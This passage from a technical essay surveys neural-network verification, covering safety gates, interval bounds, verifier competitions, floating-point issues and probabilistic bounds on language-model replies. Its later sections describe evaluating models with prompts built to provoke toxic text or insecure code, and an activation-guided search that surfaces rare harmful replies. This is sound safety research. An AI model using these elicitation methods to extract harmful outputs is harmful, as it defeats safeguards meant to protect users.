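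Zongo and Wei think the gate failed because it checked only one second ahead and interrupted manoeuvres the network would have carried out over several seconds. It also lacked a proven fallback. The drones couldn't leave their routes or fly slower than 7.5 metres per second, so passing the check for the next second didn't show that they could still avoid each other afterwards. The gate also predicted the effect of one drone's command as if the other drone would hold its speed.

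Zongo and Wei still credit this kind of gate with a guarantee that doesn't depend on the network. But near-collisions still occurred with the gate in these simulations, which shouldn't have happened if its assumptions had held. Correcting the positions worked much better but offers no such guarantee, because it relies on the network to respond sensibly. Training the gate's safety function together with the network might improve the gate, but somebody would then have to prove the learned function correct.

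## Proving facts about the model itself

A wrapper that distrusts its model pays for this with run-time checks, refusals and fallbacks. The alternative is to rely on a promise, as a library does with an unsafe trait. For a model with weights *w*, the promise could be

∀*x* ∈ *X*: *f*(*x*; *w*) ∈ *Y*

The guarantee is that every input in a set *X* produces an output in *Y*, the set of acceptable outputs. Nobody can tell whether this is true by reading the model's weights, so a program called a neural network verifier has to prove it.

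### A network with two hidden neurons

Suppose a tiny network sets the delivery cart's speed from two sensor readings, *x*₁ and *x*₂, each between 0 and 1:

*h*₁ = max(0, *x*₁ + *x*₂)

*h*₂ = max(0, *x*₁ − *x*₂)

*y* = *h*₁ − *h*₂

The forbidden event is again a speed outside the range 0 to 2. The verifier can't try every pair of readings, but it can work out the lowest and highest value that each quantity could take, one layer at a time:

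| Quantity | Lowest | Highest |
|---|---|---|
| *x*₁ + *x*₂ | 0 | 2 |
| *x*₁ − *x*₂ | −1 | 1 |
| *h*₁ | 0 | 2 |
| *h*₂ | 0 | 1 |
| *y* | 0 − 1 = −1 | 2 − 0 = 2 |

This proves that the speed never exceeds 2, but it doesn't prove that the cart never reverses, which is also true. The lower bound is too pessimistic because the calculation combines *h*₁ = 0 with *h*₂ = 1. These can't happen together, since *h*₁ is 0 only when both readings are 0 and *h*₂ is 1 only when *x*₁ is 1.

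Splitting the problem into two cases fixes this. If *x*₁ is at least *x*₂, then *h*₂ is *x*₁ − *x*₂, and *y* simplifies to 2*x*₂. Otherwise *h*₂ is 0 and *y* is *x*₁ + *x*₂. Both expressions stay between 0 and 2, so the network satisfies the required property.

Every neuron that could be either zero or positive may double the number of cases. With 300 such neurons, there could be 2³⁰⁰ cases, about 10⁹⁰. The best verifiers avoid most of the splitting into cases by bounding each neuron with a linear formula in the inputs. Unlike a plain interval, the formula preserves information about how the neurons depend on each other. The verifiers split a case only if the bounds are still too loose.

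### Sound and complete verifiers

A verifier can answer true, false or unknown. *No Soundness in the Real World* (2025) defines a verifier as sound if the property holds whenever the verifier answers true, and complete if the verifier answers true whenever the property holds. Soundness here describes a verifier's answers, not a Rust interface. The interval calculation is sound but incomplete, since it couldn't rule out reversing. A verifier that always answers "unknown" is also sound.

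Some tools are unsound. SobolBox, for instance, searches for inputs that produce extreme outputs and reports that a property holds if it finds no violation. Its developer calls these verdicts high-confidence but unsound. They are test results, so a wrapper that needs a guarantee shouldn't rely on them.

### What verifiers can handle

Neural network verification has an annual competition. *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)* (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, 2025) reports eight teams, and *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) reports eleven teams with 13 tools.

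The winner, α,β-CROWN, settled 3,164 of the 3,373 problems in the main track. It proved 1,982 properties and found counterexamples to the other 1,182. Vibecheck came second, settling 3,108. Its developers built it in two months with Claude Code, mostly using Claude Opus 4.8.

These are α,β-CROWN's results on six of the benchmarks:

| Task of the network | Weights | Inputs | Proved | Refuted | Open |
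|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Advising aircraft how to avoid a collision | 13,000 | 5 | 139 | 47 | 0 |
| Database and video-streaming functions | 33,000 to 37 million | 1 to 308 | 194 | 0 | 0 |
| Certifying that a controller is safe | 1,000 to 4,000 | 2 to 6 | 6 | 6 | 0 |
| Classifying photographs (VGG16) | 138 million | 150,528 | 18 | 0 | 0 |
| Recognising traffic signs | 0.9 to 1.8 million | 2,700 to 12,000 | 0 | 36 | 9 |
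| Classifying small images (transformers) | 68,000 to 76,000 | 3,072 | 123 | 0 | 77 |

The number of weights is a poor guide to how hard a network's properties are to prove. VGG16 is by far the largest network here, but some of its 18 properties let only a single pixel change, which makes them easier to check. The transformers are tiny, with two or three layers, but the winner still left 77 of 200 problems unsolved. Transformers, the kind of network behind language models, use operations that are harder to bound than sums and maxima.

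Another tool, ACT, reported proofs for all 200 transformer problems, far more than the other tools. The benchmark is poor at exposing a verifier that wrongly reports properties as proved, because its designers had removed most of the problems with known counterexamples. ACT also had ten answers marked wrong on other benchmarks.

Like Lean's kernels, verifiers have bugs. Eight of the 13 tools gave at least one answer that the organisers counted as incorrect or that lacked a valid counterexample. One tool gave 955 such answers, partly because of a last-minute bug in how it wrote its counterexamples. Even α,β-CROWN gave one. In the long term, the organisers want tools to accompany each positive verdict with a proof that a much simpler program could check.

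### How much of the input space a proof covers

The cart network's proof covers every reading its sensors can produce, while most proofs about image networks cover only a small region around one picture. They typically show that the network's answer stays the same if no pixel's brightness changes by more than a small amount.

For the digit-reading network, allowing each of the 784 pixels to change by one level gives up to 3⁷⁸⁴ images, or about 10³⁷⁴. No test could try them all, but they are still a tiny share of all possible images, and the proof doesn't cover the rest. The proof also doesn't show that the network's answer for the original image was right, because that depends on a person looking at the image and labeling it.

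Even these local properties often fail. One of the competition's networks classifies 83.5% of its test images correctly. For 66.0% of them, α,β-CROWN could also prove that the answer stays correct under any change of up to 2/255 of the brightness range in each colour value. The network had been trained in a way designed to make such proofs easier.

A wrapper can make up for a limited input range if it can recognise when an input is outside it:

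```rust
pub fn cart_speed(net: &VerifiedNet, x1: f64, x2: f64) -> f64 {
    let covered = (0.0..=1.0).contains(&x1)
        && (0.0..=1.0).contains(&x2);
    if covered { net.run(x1, x2) } else { 0.0 }
}
```

If a broken sensor returns 7 or NaN, the cart stops, so the guarantee holds for every pair of numbers. The same method is useless for photographs; a wrapper could compare each new picture with a list of pictures that have proofs, but almost no picture from a real camera would be close enough to any of them.

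### Real arithmetic and floating-point arithmetic

Most verifiers treat a network's arithmetic as exact, but computers round. *No Soundness in the Real World* gives the example of 2⁵³ + 1 − 2⁵³, which equals 1. In double precision, rounding down, a computer working left to right gets 0, because it can't represent 2⁵³ + 1 and drops the 1. If it subtracts before adding the 1, it gets 1. A network's output can therefore depend on the order in which a particular chip adds numbers, which the weights don't determine.

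A rounding error can also break a property that looks obvious. In real arithmetic, the SoftSign function, which some networks use in place of max(0, *x*), never decreases as its input grows, but *Floating-Point Neural Network Verification at the Software Level* (2025) shows that the usual 32-bit version sometimes does. A proof that a network's output never falls when an input rises could therefore be correct in real arithmetic but not hold for the program. Ordinary use might never reveal the failure, but an attacker who understands the rounding could search for inputs that cause it.

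To handle such cases, the competition's organisers run each reported counterexample through one fixed version of one program, and they don't penalise a tool if the output misses the forbidden region by no more than 0.0001. They acknowledge that this makes results repeatable but doesn't settle what the network "really" does near a boundary.

Some verifiers account for rounding. PyRAT's developers, whose tool came third, say its results are sound for floating-point arithmetic when it runs on an ordinary processor. Another approach is to prove a stronger property than necessary, for example that the speed stays below 1.99, and then prove separately that rounding can't add 0.01. An output check doesn't have this problem, because it tests the number the computer actually produced.

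### Why language models are harder

For a language model, "every input" means every prompt. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens (words or pieces of words), there are 10⁵⁰ prompts of ten tokens. *From Transformers to Weighted Automata* (2026) points out that a sound verifier that treats the model as a black box may have to try all of them in the worst case.

A verifier that analyzes the model's internals could in principle cover many prompts at once, as the interval calculation did with sensor readings. In *The Misery of Mechanistic Interpretability*, Ladner and Althoff (2026) tried this on sentences with some words replaced by synonyms. The model represents each token as a list of numbers, so the verifier can enclose all of a word's synonyms in one region. But they had to work on one layer at a time, because verifiers don't yet scale to a whole language model, even GPT-2, which dates from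 2019.

Better tools might not help much with this kind of property, because it is often false. Replacing one word with a synonym changed GPT-2's next-word prediction in 21% of cases.

### BEAVER

*BEAVER* (Wadhwa, Suresh and colleagues, 2025) addresses the narrower question of how likely a model's reply to one given prompt is to have a certain property. A language model assigns a probability to every possible next token, so the probability of a whole reply is the product of its tokens' probabilities. An oracle, which can be any deterministic program, decides whether a reply has the property.

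Suppose a visitor asks a model for a building's door code, and the property to prove is that the reply doesn't contain the code. The reply starts with "No" with probability 0.7, the code with probability 0.2, and something else with probability 0.1.

1. At first nothing is known, so the probability of an acceptable reply is between 0 and 1.
2. No later token can take the code back, so every reply that begins with it is a violation. The upper bound falls to 0.8.
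3. BEAVER runs the model again to see what follows "No". With probability 0.9 the reply ends there, which gives an acceptable reply with probability 0.7 × 0.9 = 0.63. This becomes the lower bound.

The true probability is now certain to be between 0.63 and 0.8. The gap of 0.17 belongs to unfinished replies, 0.07 that begin with "No" and 0.1 that begin with something else. In general,

lower bound = total probability of replies known to be acceptable

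upper bound = 1 − total probability of replies known to be violations

BEAVER always extends the most probable unfinished reply. Wadhwa and colleagues prove that no other order resolves all replies above a given probability with fewer runs of the model. The bounds are valid no matter when the process stops.

The tests covered five open-weight models (models whose weights anyone can download) with 4 to 70 billion weights. Each task had 300 prompts, each combining a request with instructions meant to provoke bad behaviour. Replies were at most 16 or 32 tokens long. A prompt counted as safe if at least 90% of the probability went to acceptable replies, and as risky if less did. If the bounds on that probability were too far apart to tell, the prompt remained undecided.

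| Model | Toxic text: safe / risky / open | Insecure code: safe / risky / open |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-4B | 142 / 54 / 104 | 54 / 103 / 143 |
| Gemma-3-12B | 1 / 281 / 18 | 59 / 117 / 124 |
| Qwen2.5-14B | 0 / 262 / 38 | 19 / 120 / 161 |
| Qwen3-30B-A3B | 74 / 93 / 133 | 57 / 97 / 146 |
| Llama-3.3-70B | 1 / 279 / 20 | 25 / 155 / 120 |

Each prompt took about two minutes. A method that drew random replies and added up their probabilities found fewer of the prompts that risked producing toxic text, by a factor of up to 7.6, even though it ran the model more times.

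Proving bounds for a model with 70 billion weights is impressive. But a "safe" prompt may still produce a toxic reply one time in ten, and the number of replies to explore grows quickly with their length.

### Proven lower bounds on harm

In *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models*, Nazeri, Schmuck and colleagues (2026) search for harmful replies that are too rare to turn up in ordinary sampling. They collect 64 harmful and 64 harmless replies to a prompt. The average difference in the model's activations between the two groups gives a direction that tends to accompany harmful replies. The search then favours unfinished replies that are probable and far along this direction. If the direction is misleading, the search finds less, but the total probability of the harmful replies it has found is still a valid lower bound on the probability of a harmful reply to that prompt.

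In one test, a user asked Llama 3.2, a model with 3 billion weights, for software to break into a neighbour's Wi-Fi. The oracle counted a reply as harmful if it named any of three programs. Ordinary sampling, limited to 1,000 tokens, found no harmful reply. In one setting, the search proved that the probability of a harmful reply was at least 4.3 × 10⁻⁸. The upper bound of 9.2% was about two million times higher and was only a statistical estimate with 95% confidence.

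Closing that gap by sampling is expensive. If *n* random replies are all harmless, the upper bound at 95% confidence is

1 − 0.025^(1/*n*)

Getting this down to one in a million takes about 3.7 million harmless replies to a single prompt. Wadhwa and colleagues object that a method with only a proven lower bound can show that a model is unsafe but never that it is safe.

### What the bounds leave out

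Bounds for 300 prompts don't establish anything about other prompts, so they fall short of the restated criterion. Wadhwa and colleagues extend their results statistically by drawing the prompts at random from a defined collection. They conclude with 95% confidence that for each model, at least 42% of the prompts in their privacy collection are risky, meaning that the model reveals a leaked email address more than 10% of the time. This result doesn't cover prompts outside the collection, which an attacker can choose.

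A more basic obstacle is that the formula that turns a language model's scores into probabilities never gives exactly zero. If the program samples from all the tokens, every possible reply has some chance of appearing, including every forbidden one, so verification cannot prove that a forbidden reply will never appear. Ordinary code has to exclude those replies, for example by blocking certain tokens or checking the finished text.

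The oracle also limits what these results prove. For toxic text, Wadhwa and colleagues used Detoxify, which is itself a learned model, so their bounds apply only to what Detoxify classifies as toxic. Nazeri and colleagues used a list of names, so a reply that warned against using one of the listed programs would still count as a match. Wadhwa and colleagues respond that ordinary benchmarks depend on the same oracles, which is true, but benchmark scores aren't presented as guarantees.

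If an oracle is good enough, a wrapper can use it to check every reply. BEAVER's bounds would still help estimate how often the wrapper would refuse. They matter more for models with public weights, because anyone who downloads such a model can remove the wrapper.

### Certificates checked during operation

For machines, the useful promise is often about where a controller's actions lead over time. The cart's gate relied on the rule that the distance to the wall, *d*, must be at least the stopping distance, *v*²/2. As a function of the cart's state, this is

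*B*(*d*, *v*) = *d* − *v*²/2

*B* is a barrier function, a kind of certificate. It has to meet three conditions:

- *B* is at least 0 in every state where the machine may start.
- *B* is negative in every unsafe state, such as reaching the wall while still moving.
- Wherever *B* is at least 0, the machine's motion never takes it below 0.

A machine that satisfies all three can't reach an unsafe state. When the cart brakes at 1 m/s², *d* and *v*²/2 shrink at the same rate, so *B* stays constant.

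Few machines have such a simple formula, so engineers often train a second network to serve as *B*. They don't need to trust the training process, but somebody must then prove that the trained network meets the conditions in every state. The competition's certificate benchmark does this for states with two to six dimensions. Proofs quickly become impractical as the number of dimensions grows. If a proof needs 100 points along each dimension, it needs 10¹² points for six dimensions.

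*Formal Verification of Neural Certificates Done Dynamically* (Henzinger, Kueffner and Yu, 2025) avoids most of this work by verifying only the states that the machine might soon reach. At each step, one program computes a region certain to contain the machine's path for a short time, and a verifier checks the certificate throughout that region. If the check fails, the monitor signals the fallback.

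The machine keeps moving during each check. If the monitor checks the machine every *ε* seconds and the fallback needs *h* seconds, each check must cover the next 2*ε* + *h* seconds and finish in less than *ε*. For a cart that takes 2 seconds to stop and a monitor that checks it every 0.1 seconds, each check must cover the next 2.2 seconds and finish in under 0.1 seconds. Henzinger and colleagues prove that, with this timing, a passed check guarantees the certificate's conditions for at least the next *h* seconds. They demonstrated the method on a satellite approaching another object in orbit.

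This covers every state that matters at the time, but the guarantee doesn't extend to the whole future, so the monitor must keep renewing it. As with a gate, the machine still needs a working fallback and an accurate model of its motion.

### When the weights change

A proof applies to one set of weights. If retraining changes the last line of the cart's network to *y* = *h*₁ − 2*h*₂, readings of 1 and 0 give a speed of −1, and the cart reverses. The network may still give much the same test results.

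For small networks this is manageable, because developers can run the verifier again. α,β-CROWN took about two seconds on many of the aircraft properties, so the check could be part of every release. The wrapper should also compare a fingerprint of the weights with the one recorded in the proof before loading them. Otherwise, replacing the weights file could silently break a guarantee that other code relies on.

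### Where a proof is enough

A proof of this kind can replace distrust of the model when the network is small and fixed, its inputs are a few numbers whose ranges the wrapper can check, the promise can be stated as an exact formula, and the proof holds for the arithmetic the computer actually performs. The best candidates are simple controllers, networks that replace large lookup tables of advice for aircraft, and some database components.

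A learned index, for example, predicts where a key is in a sorted list. If a verifier proves that the prediction is never more than 50 places off for any key in a given range, a program needs to search only 101 places. The competition's tools handle such networks well, although the benchmark's designers first had to replace a tree of small networks with one larger network, because a choice between networks was hard to verify.

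Even for these components, a run-time check is often simpler. Limiting the cart's speed takes one line of code and works for any weights. A proof is worth the trouble when the check would be too slow, when no acceptable fallback exists, or when the promise relates the outputs for several inputs. For example, an estimate of how many records match a database query should never fall when the query becomes broader. Checking one query and its estimate can't show whether the network meets this requirement.

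None of the conditions hold for a language model that answers questions. *Science of Safe AI* notes that formal verification often can't handle properties that depend on meaning, because they usually can't be written as formulas, a problem that a faster verifier wouldn't solve.
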